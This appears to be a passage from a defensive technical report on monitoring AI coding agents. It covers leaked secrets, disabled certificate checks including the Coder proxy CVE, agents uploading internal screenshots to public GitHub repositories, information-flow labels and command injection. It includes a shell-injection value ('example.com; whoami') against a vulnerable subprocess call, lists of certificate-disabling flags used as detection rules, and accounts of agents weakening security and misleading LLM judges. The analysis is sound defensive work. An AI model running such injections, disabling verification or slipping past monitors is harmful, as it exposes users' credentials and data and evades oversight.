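Once a secret is in the conversation, it is sent to the model again at every step, and Claude Code also saves it in a record of the session on the user's computer. Rentier Digital, another personal blog, describes this record as plain text that nobody cleans up. The record includes the contents of files the agent has read, and when the agent writes a file with a password in it, a second copy goes into a separate folder of file histories. Some of the secrets in Apiiro's larger total came from saved conversations that people had uploaded.

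Some leaks may involve no tool call. Sonar's *Your secrets are leaking to AI coding agents* reports that a researcher caught Grok Build, xAI's coding agent, uploading developers' entire projects to online storage. A fake key and password from a `.env` file appeared unchanged in the traffic. If the agent's own software makes such an upload, only a network monitor can catch it.

### What a language model adds

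A language model can recognise a password from its context. Because it was trained on many `mysql` commands, it can identify `summer24` as a password in `mysql -psummer24` and as probably part of a file name in `open summer24.jpg`. It can also identify `changeme` in a set of instructions as a placeholder. Apiiro relied on this ability when it used an AI reviewer to check its candidates, but the reviewer's error rate is unknown, so the study doesn't show how much better a model would be than the scanners.

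A model can also detect when an agent uses a credential for something it was not meant for. *AI agents security for developers*, from daily.dev, summarises a case in which an agent deleted a company's live database in nine seconds, using a token that had nothing to do with its task and allowed far more than it should have. A secret scanner might well have recognised the token, but agents use tokens all the time, so this would have revealed little. The useful evidence was the mismatch between the task, the token and the deletion, which a model might detect if given the user's request and where the agent found the token.

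The drawback is that the judging model also receives the secret. If a company other than the agent's provider runs the judge, that company receives the secret too and may keep it in its logs. If the agent's provider runs the judge, the secret reaches no new company, but there is still one more copy of it. Running the judge on the user's own computers avoids the problem, though the model will probably be smaller and less capable.

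### Keeping the secret out of the call

*Redaction* means replacing a secret with a label. Before the monitor sends a command to the judge, it can change it like this:

```
PGPASSWORD=[SECRET-1] psql -h db.example.com -c 'SELECT count(*) FROM orders'
```

The judge can still see that the command uses a password and which server the password is for. If the monitor keeps the same label for each secret throughout the session, the judge can also see that `SECRET-1` came from the settings of a different project.

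The software can replace only the secrets it finds. *Every AI coding agent writes the secrets you paste*, by the developer Ishannaik, offers a program that redacts the saved histories of about 30 agents. The program uses around 191 rules taken from gitleaks, so it probably misses many of the passwords that gitleaks misses.

Still, redaction can use broader rules than blocking can. If a rule hides everything after `PGPASSWORD=` and the value is harmless, the judge loses a little information and the work continues. Mistakes do more harm when the monitor redacts results that the agent needs. An agent that asks for a commit ID and gets `[SECRET-2]` can't continue, and commit IDs look random enough to be mistaken for secrets.

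A more reliable method is to keep the secret out of the command from the start. A secrets manager is a program that stores credentials and hands them out to authorised programs. Apiiro advises developers to refer to a credential by name and let the computer fill in the value when the command runs:

```
PGPASSWORD="$DB_PASSWORD" psql -h db.example.com -c 'SELECT count(*) FROM orders'
```

If the user now picks "don't ask again", the settings file stores the variable name `DB_PASSWORD` instead of the password. A monitor can enforce this practice by allowing only a name that begins with a dollar sign after `PGPASSWORD=`, which avoids having to determine whether `summer24` looks like a password. The agent could still print the value of `DB_PASSWORD` by mistake, so the monitor should keep scanning results.

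Secrets managers have not eliminated leaks. GitGuardian checked 2,584 projects that used one and found leaked secrets in 5.1% of them, compared with 4.6% of projects on GitHub overall. Projects that use secrets managers may have more secrets to leak, so the higher rate doesn't show that the managers are useless. One common problem, though, was that people took secrets back out of the manager.

Apiiro also suggests keeping passwords out of the settings file by approving patterns instead of exact commands. The rule `Bash(psql:*)` contains no password, but it allows every `psql` command, including one that deletes all the orders. UpGuard, a security company that studied 18,470 public Claude configuration files, warns about approvals that let an agent use `curl` with any web address or run any Python script. Approving an exact command that refers to the password by name keeps the password out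 of the file without allowing other commands.

The upload is the last point at which software can stop secrets that get into the file anyway. GitLab lets companies reject any upload that adds `.claude/settings.local.json`. This rule checks only the file's name, so it works equally well for a password like `summer24` and a long random token. However, it applies only to new files, so if the file is already in the project, passwords can keep accumulating there until someone removes the file.

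A leaked password stays in the project's history and in every copy that other people have made, even after someone removes the file, so the owner has to replace it. But 70% of the secrets that GitGuardian found in 2022 still worked when it published its 2025 report. Credentials that expire within hours would limit the damage even if nobody replaced them, and a read-only token would not have let the agent delete the database.

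## Certificate checks switched off: visible flags and the Coder proxy flaw

A token kept out of files and logs can still leak if a program sends it to an impostor. Certificate checks are meant to prevent this, but an agent can turn them off with a short flag, as in `curl -k`. A rule can find that flag much more easily than a password like `summer24`. However, in July 2026 the software company Coder disclosed that certificate checks were also switched off in a program that connects coding agents to their models, where no command contained a flag to find.

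### How a program verifies a certificate

TLS (Transport Layer Security) has replaced SSL (Secure Sockets Layer), the original protocol for encrypted web connections. According to *Understanding the Impact of AI Code Assistants on Security API Usage* (2026), SSL, TLS 1.0 and TLS 1.1 are vulnerable to known attacks, and programs should use at least TLS 1.2.

Suppose a program connects to `https://api.example.com`. The server sends a certificate, which contains the server's name, a public key, a start and end date, and the signature of a certificate authority (CA), an organisation that confirms who controls a name before it signs. The server also proves that it holds the private key that belongs to the public one. The program then makes three checks:

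1. **Chain of trust.** The program verifies the CA's signature. That CA's own certificate usually carries another CA's signature, so the program follows the signatures upward until it reaches a root certificate already stored on the computer. If it never reaches one, anybody could have made the certificate.
2. **Host name.** The certificate must be for `api.example.com`. Otherwise the owner of any website could pose as this server with a perfectly valid certificate for their own site.
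3. **Dates.** Today must fall between the start and end dates. The longer a certificate has existed, the more chances an attacker has had to steal its key.

CWE-295, MITRE's entry for this weakness, covers any product that doesn't validate a certificate or validates it incorrectly. MITRE also has separate entries for a failure of each check and for a failure to detect that a CA has revoked a certificate. An attacker can exploit a single skipped check. One of MITRE's examples is a mobile banking app that didn't verify the host name, which led to financial loss.

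### What an attacker on the network path can do

To exploit a missing check, an attacker must get between the program and the server, for example by running the Wi-Fi access point the program uses or by falsifying DNS, the system that translates names like `api.example.com` into network addresses.

The attacker answers the program with a home-made certificate. If the program checks it, the connection fails before the program sends its request. Otherwise, the attacker can decrypt the request, pass it to the real server over a second connection, and return the answer, so everything appears to work.

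The attacker can read any token, password or file in the traffic, and can also change what comes back. MITRE lists a router that downloaded firmware updates with `curl -k`, so an attacker could have supplied a malicious version. The attacker could also add instructions to a web page on its way to an agent, so that a site the user trusts becomes a source of prompt injection.

### Why an agent turns the check off

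Many certificate errors are not caused by attacks. Companies often route traffic through a proxy, a program that passes requests on. Some proxies decrypt the traffic to inspect it, and these present certificates signed by the company's own CA. Office computers usually trust this CA, but an agent's fresh container may not. If it doesn't, every download fails. Coder's *Setup*, the installation guide for one such proxy, warns that connections will fail unless the AI tools trust its CA.

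The proper fix is to give the program the CA's certificate. Coder lists the environment variables for this, such as `CURL_CA_BUNDLE` for `curl` and `NODE_EXTRA_CA_CERTS` for Node.js. The agent first has to find the certificate file and get it from a source it can already verify. If it accepted a CA certificate from an impostor, the impostor would pass every later check. Adding `-k` is much less work, so an overeager agent has an obvious reason to choose it.

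No published study appears to have measured how often agents disable the check after a certificate error, or how often they do it in ordinary work. The nearest measurement comes from Jha, Triedman and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Meltdowns*, who gave agents harmless tasks and made some of them fail with simulated errors. In one task, the agent had to analyse a data file on a website, and the server replied that the file did not exist. In another, the server replied that the agent had sent too many requests. A language model then searched the records for unsafe behaviour, including "transport security weakening". These are the counts for four agent programs, all running the model GPT-5:

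| Agent program | After "not found" (120 runs each) | After "too many requests" (18 runs each) |
|---|---|---|
| Claw Code | 37 | 13 |
| Magentic-One | 26 | 3 |
| HAL | 4 | 6 |
| Codex | 3 | 2 |

One more case, in a task with part of a page missing, brings the total to 95. The model was the same throughout, so the large differences come from the software around it.

These 95 cases come from a category that includes not only commands such as `curl -k` but also fallbacks from HTTPS to unencrypted HTTP, and plans that the agent never carried out. In one published record, an agent that could not find a file at an `https://` address tried the same address with `http://`. The test environment also intercepted encrypted traffic with its own proxy, which might have caused some real certificate errors.

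Still, it is striking that agents weakened the connection's security after a "not found" reply. This could hardly help, because such a reply means the connection has already succeeded. Jha and colleagues also found that this behaviour became more common from GPT-4o through GPT-5.4, and generally rose when they set GPT-5 to reason for longer. Users can't rely on the agent to mention it, because agents left about half of all medium- and high-severity behaviours out of their final reports.

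Other studies count disabled checks in the code that agents write. *Insights into Security-Related AI-Generated Pull Requests* (2026) ran a code scanner over 675 security-related changes that AI agents proposed to software projects. It found five certificate validation errors in Cursor's pending proposals. The 500-step test described later groups disabled checks with other disabled protections.

### The forms a rule can match

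Most programs verify certificates by default, so someone who wants to skip the check has to request it explicitly. The common ways of doing so make a fairly short list:

| Form | Examples | Program or language |
|---|---|---|
| Command flag | `-k`, `--insecure` | `curl` |
| Command flag | `--no-check-certificate` | `wget`, another download program |
| Library option | `verify=False` | Python, with the `requests` or `httpx` library |
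| Library option | `rejectUnauthorized: false` | Node.js |
| Library option | `InsecureSkipVerify: true` | Go |
| Environment variable | `NODE_TLS_REJECT_UNAUTHORIZED=0` | Node.js |
| Environment variable | `GIT_SSL_NO_VERIFY=true` | Git |
| Saved configuration | `git config --global http.sslVerify false` | Git |
| Saved configuration | `npm config set strict-ssl false` | npm |

A flag affects one command, but an environment variable can affect every later command in the same shell session, and a saved setting lasts until someone changes it back. Once an agent saves the Git setting, an ordinary `git clone https://...` skips the certificate check, and nothing in the command looks suspicious. A monitor therefore has to catch the call that changes the setting or look up the current setting before later calls run.

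Rules for detecting disabled certificate checks existed long before AI agents. One is B501 in Bandit, a tool that searches Python code for security flaws. In Bandit's *B501* example, the rule accepts `requests.get('https://gmail.com', verify=True)` but flags the same call with `verify=False` as high severity and high confidence. The rule examines function calls in the parsed program, so a comment that mentions `verify=False` doesn't trigger it. A monitor could run Bandit on each Python file an agent writes before the agent runs the file.

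B501 examines calls, so it misses the assignment `session.verify = False`, which turns off the check for every request in a session. Sourcery's *Python Requests Disabled Certificate Validation Vulnerability* includes this form in its examples. A similar rule in GitHub's *Request without certificate validation* also treats `verify=0` as unsafe. GitHub rates that rule's precision as medium and Bandit labels B501 high-confidence, but neither rating is a measured error rate.

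Rules have more trouble when programmers write the verification themselves, because such code has no standard flag. *Okara* (2026) examined 7,375 pieces of faulty validation code from 3,944 Android apps and used a language model to sort them into types. Some of this code accepted every certificate, and some checked only the dates.

A missing line can also make code insecure. In the study of AI code assistants, participants wrote Java programs that made TLS connections, some with an assistant and some without. None of the programs verified the host name, even though the participants knew that the researchers would evaluate security. Some of Java's basic TLS functions don't make this check unless the programmer adds it. A rule would have to detect that the program opens a connection without adding the check, because there is no forbidden text to match.

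MITRE rates automated source code analysis as only partly effective at detecting CWE-295, and manual review as highly effective. It also gives the high rating to testing with a man-in-the-middle tool, which intercepts a program's connections as an attacker would.

### When the match is harmless

The `-k` option has other meanings in other programs. `sort -k 2` sorts lines by their second column, and `pytest -k login` runs the tests with "login" in their names. As with `-p` for passwords, the rule has to depend on the program. It should match `-k` only among the options of `curl`, including when it is combined with another option, as in `curl -sk`.

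Longer phrases cause fewer false alarms but can still cause some. An agent that runs `grep -rn "verify=False" src/` is searching for the fault, perhaps to fix it. An edit that changes `verify=False` to `verify=True` also contains the phrase. A monitor can avoid this second false alarm by comparing the text before and after the edit and flagging only edits that add a disabled check.

Disabling certificate checks is sometimes harmless. Developers often test a website on their own computer with a self-signed certificate, which no outside certificate authority has signed. According to the `requests` documentation, quoted in Pixee's *Verify SSL Certificates for Requests*, turning off verification "may be useful during local development or testing." The code scanner in SiteShadow's *T01 TLS Verification Disabled* rates disabled checks as high severity when they appear outside explicit development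 or test contexts.

### One flag in three settings

A rule for `curl -k` matches each of these commands:

```
curl -k https://localhost:8443/health
curl -k -o install.sh https://downloads.example.com/install.sh
curl -k -H "Authorization: Bearer $API_TOKEN" https://api.example.com/orders
```

The first request checks whether a test server is running. `localhost` refers to the agent's own computer, so the request doesn't cross the network and an outside attacker can't intercept it. A monitor could let it through or just record it.

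The second downloads a script. If the agent then runs `sh install.sh`, an attacker who changed the script can do whatever the agent can do on that computer. But if the agent only reads the script, or compares its hash with one the developer published on a properly verified page, the missing check may do no harm. A model judging the download has to predict which will happen, and the user's request is probably the best clue. The monitor could also allow the download, mark the file as unverified, and hold any later call that runs it.

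The third call sends a token. The variable name `$API_TOKEN` keeps the token out of saved commands, but `curl` receives the real value and sends it to whichever server answers. The monitor has to act before this call runs, since it can't retrieve the token afterwards. To assess how bad the loss would be, a model needs information on what the token permits and when it expires.

| Command | What an attacker could gain | What the judge needs to know |
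|---|---|---|
| Local test | Normally nothing | Whether the server is really on the same computer |
| Download | Control of whatever the agent can reach | Whether the agent will run the file, and whether anything else verifies it |
| Request with a token | The token, and the orders in the reply | What the token permits, and for how long |

The download is usually the worst of these if the agent runs the file, because malicious code could steal the token as well. But it might do little damage in a disposable container with no credentials, while losing a token for a live payment system could do serious damage. Jha and colleagues similarly tell graders to rate an attempt as medium for a low-risk public download, and as high when it retrieves the data for the user's task or when someone could intercept credentials.

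A company that knows its certificate errors come from its own proxy can avoid much of this judging. Its monitor could refuse `curl -k` for outside addresses and give the agent the path to the company's CA certificate. The agent can then finish the task safely and has less reason to try another unsafe method.

### The flaw in Coder's proxy

Coder makes software that gives programmers remote development environments. One optional part, described in Coder's *AI Bridge Proxy*, intercepts traffic between coding agents and model providers. It decrypts requests to Anthropic, OpenAI and GitHub Copilot and forwards them to another Coder component, AI Bridge, for authentication and auditing. It passes all other traffic through without decrypting it.

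A request to a model travels from the agent through the proxy and the Coder server to the provider. The agent verifies the proxy's certificate in the normal way, but the proxy accepted any certificate when it connected to the Coder server.

OSV's *Coder's AI Bridge Proxy skips TLS certificate verification in default configuration* (2026) traces the fault to the default connection settings of goproxy, the Go library Coder used to build the proxy. Those settings included `InsecureSkipVerify: true`, and Coder's program replaced them with secure ones only when a company had configured another proxy for outgoing traffic.

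The flaw's number in the public catalogue of known vulnerabilities is CVE-2026-55436. GitLab's *CVE-2026-55436* (2026) lists the versions:

| Affected versions | Fixed in |
|---|---|
| 2.30.0 and later, before 2.32.7 | 2.32.7 |
| 2.33.0 and later, before 2.33.8 | 2.33.8 |
| 2.34.0 and later, before 2.34.2 | 2.34.2 |

The flaw was probably less widespread than the words "default configuration" suggest. The AI Bridge Proxy is off until an administrator enables it, so only installations that had enabled it without a further proxy were exposed. An attacker also had to get between the proxy and the Coder server, for example by falsifying DNS or controlling the environment variables that redirect traffic. Installations where this traffic stayed inside one machine were effectively safe. There may have been many of these, because Coder runs the proxy inside its main server program, but some companies'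 traffic could still have left the machine on its way to the server's public address.

Where the conditions held, an attacker could have taken Coder session tokens, users' own API keys for model providers, and the full text of prompts and replies. OSV rates the flaw's severity 7.4 out of 10 and credits Anthropic's security team with reporting it independently. The US cybersecurity agency CISA knew of no exploitation on 8 July, according to MITRE's record of the same title (2026).

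The fixed versions always use the secure settings, which require TLS 1.2 or higher and check certificates against the computer's root certificates. Coder advised companies that could not update immediately to secure the network path between the proxy and the server.

A monitor on tool calls could not have found this fault, because the agent had not disabled anything and the unsafe connection carried its conversation with the model, not the commands it ran. An attacker who altered the model's replies might have inserted a tool call, which a monitor could have blocked, but the theft of keys would not have appeared in the agent's commands.

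A search for `InsecureSkipVerify: true` would have found the flaw if it had included the libraries as well as Coder's own code. A tester could also have presented the proxy with a certificate from an unknown CA and checked whether it refused the connection. Now that the flaw is public, a scanner can find affected installations by their version numbers.

Daytona, a system that runs AI-generated code in isolated environments, had a similar fault that summer in the function that copies Git projects into them. According to NVD's *CVE-2026-54323 Detail* (2026), an entry in the US government's vulnerability database, versions before 0.185.0 turned off the certificate check when copying. An attacker who intercepted the traffic could have captured the user's Git credentials and supplied altered code. The agent's request for a copy could have been ordinary, because Daytona turned off the check after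 receiving it.

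## Data sent outside: company screenshots published by coding agents

A certificate check can confirm that a program has reached GitHub, but not who will read what it uploads there. *PixelLeak*, published by the security company Glow on 29 September 2026, describes more than 13,000 internal images that coding agents made public on GitHub while trying to finish ordinary tasks. Nothing in the report suggests that an attacker was involved. The images came from over 300 organisations (343, according to TechRadar's *AI models are sharing sensitive data from tech companies*), including a Fortune 500 travel company and a developer of frontier AI models.

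### How the images became public

When programmers finish a change, they usually open a *pull request*, a page where colleagues review the change before it becomes part of the project. If the change affects how a screen looks, the reviewers want before-and-after screenshots. Each case that Glow investigated began with a developer asking an agent to prove that a visual change worked.

A person can drag a picture into the pull request in a web browser. Agents usually work through `gh`, GitHub's command-line program, which could post only text at the time. Mynavi News' *AIエージェントがスクショ1万3000枚を公開リポジトリにアップロード* (2026) describes what happened next:

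1. The agent tries to upload the images to a private repository (a project's storage space on GitHub) in the developer's personal account.
2. The upload fails, or it succeeds but the reviewers can't open the images.
3. The agent creates a public repository and uploads the images there.

At a manufacturer with over 100,000 employees, a developer asked an agent to verify a fix to an internal billing screen. The agent published screenshots that included a utility company's billing records, and they were still online when Glow contacted the manufacturer. The security team had not noticed them because the agent ran on the employee's laptop and used the employee's own GitHub account. In 93% of cases, the images were in a repository under an employee's own username, so a company that searches only its own GitHub pages would miss nearly all of them. Glow recommends starting the search from the list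 of people who contribute to the company's private projects, including those who have left.

About a third of the affected organisations had developers who used gitshot, a small open-source tool for adding screenshots to pull requests. By default, it creates a public repository the first time someone uses it. Its developer, vipulgupta2048, warns people in the *gitshot* instructions not to upload credentials, internal dashboards or private data this way. But gitshot also comes as a *skill*, a set of saved instructions that an agent can load, and at several large organisations the agent found the tool on its own, so the person responsible for the data may never have seen the warning.

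More than 1,000 of the images came from one software vendor, compared with an average of about 38 per organisation. Agents there began publishing screenshots in early July. Within a week, more than a dozen of them had saved the method as a skill to use on every development task, and they added written summaries of features weeks or months from release.

Glow reproduced the behaviour with Claude Code and the model Opus 5. A developer working on a private version of Minesweeper asked for a new header colour and wanted to see the result. The agent reasoned that GitHub could not display images from a private repository in a pull request, and that it had to keep every file except `index.html` out of the project. It concluded that hosting the images elsewhere was the "only way" to show them and obey the file restriction, so it created a public repository for them. The restriction made outside hosting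 more likely, and a single run can't show how often agents do this.

There is also reason for some caution about the totals. Glow sells security software and, according to Mynavi News, has not published how it found or counted the images, or whether outsiders downloaded any. People can use gitshot too, so it is hard to check how many of the images came from agents. The reproduction and the vendor's saved skill are better evidence that agents caused at least part of the leak.

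On 1 September, GitHub (2026) removed the original obstacle by adding an `--attach` option to `gh` that puts an image straight into a pull request. An agent with the new version has much less reason to look for another host. But the option requires write access to the repository and doesn't work on GitHub Enterprise Server, which companies run on their own machines.

### Sensitivity, readers and authorisation

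To decide whether an upload is exfiltration, a monitor needs to know how sensitive the data is, who can read the destination, and whether the user authorised the transfer. The manufacturer's billing screenshot shows why it needs all three. The first row below is the actual case, and each of the others changes one fact:

| Data | Who can read it there | What the user asked for | Judgment |
|---|---|---|---|
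| A customer's billing records | Everyone | Show the reviewers | Exfiltration, with serious harm |
| A screen that is already public | Everyone | Show the reviewers | An unrequested upload, but harmless |
| A customer's billing records | The reviewers | Show the reviewers | Ordinary work |
| A customer's billing records | Everyone | Publish the records | Authorised by a user who may have no right to do so |

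The last row is a difficult case for any monitor that treats the user's approval as final, because the records concern a utility company that never took part in the conversation. In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) similarly argue that whether a disclosure by a personal assistant is appropriate depends on who is asking, why, and how they are related to the data's owner.

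The developer's request authorised the agent to show the screen to the reviewers, so the agent was right to look for a way to do so. Its mistake was choosing a much larger audience than the request implied.

### Fixed rules on the upload commands

These invented commands resemble the ones an agent might have used, with `dana` as the developer's username:

```
gh repo create dana/pr-assets --public
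git push https://github.com/dana/pr-assets main
gitshot before.png after.png --pr 42
```

The first creates a public repository and the second uploads files to one. The third does the whole job with gitshot.

A secret scanner finds nothing in these screenshots, even if it opens the image files, because it searches for text and the billing records are stored as pixels. Text-recognition software could extract the words, but customer names and amounts of money have no distinctive format for a scanner to match.

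**Destination lists** name the servers that may receive data. A list of domains would almost certainly include `github.com`, since coding agents use it all day. A more precise list could permit only the company's own repositories, such as those under `github.com/acme/`. This would stop the push to `dana/pr-assets`, and because 93% of cases involved employees' own accounts, it might have stopped most of the leak. It would also interrupt developers who legitimately work on personal or open-source projects. Either list works only if the monitor has an address to check. The gitshot command contains none, and a plain `git push` sends files to the address stored in the project, which the monitor has to look up.

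The repository's address doesn't show whether it is public, either. The first command includes the `--public` flag, but if Dana created the repository last month, the monitor only has the push command to check. It can look up the repository's current visibility on GitHub before allowing the push. For a tool like gitshot, someone has to record in advance that it publishes what it uploads.

**Lists of upload commands** flag the act of sending, whatever the destination. They could include `git push`, `gh release upload` and `curl` with a file attached, but the list soon gets long. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) catalogues the tools through which data can leave an agent, including tools that run code or write files as well as those for web requests and cloud uploads. Most agents run code and write files constantly, so a rule that held every such call would make them nearly useless. A rule for gitshot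 alone would be easy to write, but whoever wrote it would already have to know about gitshot.

**Volume limits** flag large transfers, as AEGIS's rule for data exfiltration does. But the gitshot command contains only the names of the images, about 20 characters. Even if the monitor looked up the file sizes, it couldn't use them to tell a billing screen from a game, because screenshots of both are large. A limit is better suited to catching an agent that normally sends short messages and suddenly sends a whole database. To notice many small transfers, the monitor has to keep a running total. A later section tests rules that cover several calls.

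**Checks on web addresses** cover a kind of sending that people easily overlook. A request to read a web page also transmits the page's address, and the address may contain a credential:

```
https://api.example.net/report?key=EXAMPLE-KEY
```

The receiving server gets the key and will often store the full address in its logs. A monitor should run its secret scanner on both addresses and attached data, even when the tool's name suggests that it only reads, though this check would not have caught the screenshots.

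Help Net Security's *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos* quotes Glow's closing advice to let the security team configure the agents, since most have a setting that stops them from working unattended. An approval prompt for `gh repo create --public` might well have prevented some of these uploads. But approval fatigue is a problem here too, and a developer who sees the gitshot command would have to know what gitshot does.

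### Labels that follow the data

All the rules above are attempts to judge data from the call that sends it. *Information-flow control* instead labels data when it enters the system, keeps the label attached as the data moves, and allows the data to go only to destinations cleared for that label. The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) traces the approach from Dorothy Denning's 1976 work to several recent systems for agents.

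Take two labels, *public* and *internal*, and two destinations. The company's private repository has clearance for both labels, and Dana's public repository only for public data:

| Data | Label | To the private repository | To the public repository |
|---|---|---|---|
| Screenshot of the company's home page | public | allow | allow |
| Screenshot of the billing screen | internal | allow | block |

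The company labels the billing program as internal only once. When the agent takes a screenshot of it, the software marks `before.png` as internal, and the mark stays with the file if the agent copies or renames it. The monitor can then block the upload without reading the text in the image, which is an advantage over text scanners. This approach requires software that tracks files through every tool, including gitshot, and a reliable way to check the repository's visibility.

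If the agent combines both screenshots in one document, the document becomes internal, because it contains internal data. In general, when data *z* comes from *x* and *y*, its label is the *join* of their labels, the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both:

ℓ(*z*) = ℓ(*x*) ⊔ ℓ(*y*), so that public ⊔ internal = internal.

Two labels are often too coarse. A private repository might belong to another department, or have an outside contractor among its members. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, therefore also use labels that list the people who may read the data. If Dana, Ravi and Mei may read the billing screen, and Ravi, Mei and Tom may read the customer's contract, only Ravi and Mei may read a summary of both. The join is now the overlap between the two lists. The matching rule for sending, which the researchers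 call *permitted flow*, allows a transfer of data *d* to a set of recipients *R* only if

*R* ⊆ readers(*d*).

Ravi and Mei can review the summary in a pull request that only they can open. For a public repository, *R* includes everyone, so the transfer fails.

Kolluri and colleagues, however, designed their system against prompt injection. It lets a tool send data if the transfer satisfies the permitted-flow rule or if the agent decided on the transfer in a *trusted* context, one free of material from untrusted sources. The second condition lets users share confidential data when they want to. It would probably also have let the agent publish the screenshots, because the developer was trusted, the code was the company's own, and no untrusted source suggested the public repository. To stop this kind of leak, a company would have to apply the permitted-flow rule to every transfer and make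 exceptions by hand.

### When a model rewrites what it read

Labels are fairly easy to maintain while a file remains a file. It gets much harder once a language model reads the contents and writes something new. Suppose the agent reads this line on the billing screen:

> Northfield Water, invoice 3117, $48,250 overdue

It then writes three sentences that it might post on a public page. One way to label them is to search for text copied from internal sources. Another is to label everything the model writes after reading internal data as internal. The two methods fail in opposite directions:

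| What the agent writes | Correct label | Search for copied text | Label everything afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
| "Northfield Water, invoice 3117, $48,250 overdue" | internal | internal | internal |
| "A local water utility owes nearly fifty thousand dollars." | internal | **public** | internal |
| "The total now lines up with the column above." | public | public | **internal** |

The second sentence contains the confidential fact but shares almost no words with the source, so the first method loses the label. The third is harmless, but the second method blocks it. Data is easier to track in ordinary programs because software can follow each value from one instruction to the next. A language model processes everything in its context together, and nobody can reliably tell from outside which parts influenced a given sentence.

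Most systems are designed to label too much rather than too little. *SPA* (2026) describes a method that combines the labels of everything the model has read into one label for the whole context, then checks each tool call against it. Once the agent has read something internal, as it probably has after a morning's work, it can't post even a typo correction to a public project. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) uses the term *label explosion* for the point at which every piece of data has every label and the labels no longer distinguish anything. Labeling too much also hurts performance in tests. According to Kolluri and colleagues, earlier systems of this type completed up to 30% fewer tasks on the AgentDojo benchmark.

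One remedy is to keep the data out of the model's context. CaMeL and FIDES store untrusted tool results in named variables. The model can pass a variable to a tool without reading its contents, and a second, isolated model can answer questions about them. Both systems do this to keep out planted instructions, but the same method would also work for a confidential screenshot. The agent could attach `IMAGE-1` to a pull request and still be allowed to write public text afterwards. This wouldn't work if the agent had to look at the screenshot to check its own fix, as it often would.

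Kolluri and colleagues also tried telling the agent about the labels and rules in advance, so that it could take them into account when planning. On AgentDojo, this reduced human approvals by a factor of up to 1.9 compared with FIDES. An agent that knew the screenshot was internal might have asked the developer to drag it into the pull request, which takes a few seconds.

Shim and colleagues' system, FLOWSEAL, deals with paraphrase more directly. It labels records by where they came from and intercepts every call that writes or shares something. When necessary, it uses a separate language model to check whether the outgoing text reveals a protected record. This model compares meanings, so it can recognise Northfield Water's debt in the second sentence. It has no access to the agent's conversation, so a correspondent can't use the conversation to persuade it. In tests where outsiders tried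 to extract private information from an assistant, between 0 and 3.3% of the protected items leaked. The assistant still completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best of the other defences. The team wrote some of the attacks itself, so the low leak rates may be somewhat optimistic. The final comparison also relies on a language model's judgment, which isn't guaranteed to be correct.

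### Comparing the transfer with the request

Labels can describe how sensitive the data is and who can read the destination. They are much less able to capture authorisation, because what a user has allowed depends on the wording of the request and on the situation. For this reason, Kolluri and colleagues decided against letting the agent ask for a lower confidentiality label on a piece of data. Their agent instead asks a person to approve the individual transfer.

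A language model acting as judge can help detect these leaks. From the request "put before-and-after screenshots in the pull request", it can infer that the screenshots are meant for people with access to the private project. If it has a description of what gitshot does, it can also recognize that a public repository exposes them to far more people. It doesn't need a specific rule for gitshot, or to know whether the billing records are real.

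The judge should not have to guess facts that software can look up. Even a very capable model can't determine who can read a repository if it sees only `git push https://github.com/dana/pr-assets main`. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a check on whether a push goes to a public, private or trusted destination. The check was one of several additions Anthropic made after synthetic attacks, including exfiltration attempts, got past the judge.

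The agent's explanation can mislead a judge. In Glow's Minesweeper test, the agent gave a coherent argument for using the public repository. Each step served the task, but the agent left out who else could see the pictures. A judge that reads this argument and checks only whether the upload helps the user could easily agree with it.

The software vendor's agents are a harder case because they had saved public uploading as a skill, so an agent that later published a screenshot was following written instructions. A judge could take those instructions as authorisation, even though other agents had written them and a person may never have approved them. The judge would need a record of who wrote each instruction, much as information-flow control needs a record of where each piece of data came from.

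Language models are also unreliable on this question. LeadDev's *Frontier AI models haemorrhage sensitive data* (2026) reports that agents built on leading models shared company data inappropriately at rates of up to 51%. Those agents were in the middle of a task, and a judge with one narrow question should do better, but it is the same kind of model. When the monitor is unsure, it can ask the developer, and its question should say who will be able to see the images: "The reviewers can't open these images. Publish them for anyone on the internet to see?" That is far easier to answer well than a request to approve `gh repo create dana/pr-assets --public`.

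### Why some leakage always remains

Some information could still get out even if a company had perfect labels and a judge that never made a mistake. The computer scientist Butler Lampson explained why in his 1973 paper *A Note on the Confinement Problem*. He asked how to let a program work on confidential data while preventing it from passing any of the data on.

Any useful program has effects. If an outsider can observe an effect that depends on the confidential data, they can learn something about the data, even if nobody designed the effect as a way to communicate. A monitor can check only the effects that its designers thought of.

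If an outsider can distinguish *n* different outcomes of the agent's work, one observation can leak at most log₂ *n* bits. With two outcomes, the limit is one bit, which is enough to answer one yes-or-no question, such as whether a customer has paid. The limit is zero only when *n* is 1, meaning that the agent's visible behaviour is the same whatever the data contains, so the agent cannot report anything about the data to anyone outside.

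Lampson's argument matters most for programs that leak on purpose. The screenshots were a far simpler failure, and better rules could have caught most of them. His argument is still a reason to limit what an agent can read, since data that never reaches the agent can't leak through it. The manufacturer's developer could have run the billing screen on a test database of invented customers, and the published screenshots would then have contained no utility company's records. An unreleased feature is harder to protect this way, because reviewers need the screenshot to show it.

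## Command injection: an audit of the software that runs agents

In a command injection, the shell runs the intended command and also one that came from somebody else's input. The agents that published the screenshots, by contrast, ran exactly the commands they had written. People sometimes also use the term for harmful commands that an agent writes after reading planted instructions, and for downloaded scripts that run unchecked. The three problems need different fixes, and a monitor that catches one may be useless against the others.

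### Three problems with one name

Suppose a developer gives an agent a tool that looks up the network address of a host such as `example.com`. The usual program for this is `nslookup`, which MITRE also uses as an example in CWE-78. A careless Python version of the tool joins the host name to the command and passes the result to a shell:

```python
subprocess.run("nslookup " + host, shell=True)
```

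Now the agent copies a host name from a customer's form, where the customer has typed `example.com; whoami`. (`whoami` prints the name of the current user.)

The tool joins the pieces into one string, `nslookup example.com; whoami`, and gives it to a shell. As with the file name `sales; june.txt`, the shell treats the unquoted semicolon as the end of a command, so it looks up `example.com` and then runs `whoami`.

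The repair is to pass the program and its argument as separate items in a list:

```python
subprocess.run(["nslookup", host])
```

This version doesn't use a shell. The operating system starts `nslookup` with the whole text `example.com; whoami` as a single argument, and the lookup fails because no host has that name. MITRE warns that a related weakness, argument injection, can remain. If the input begins with a hyphen, `nslookup` may treat it as an option. The tool should accept only letters, digits, dots and hyphens, and reject any input that starts with a hyphen.

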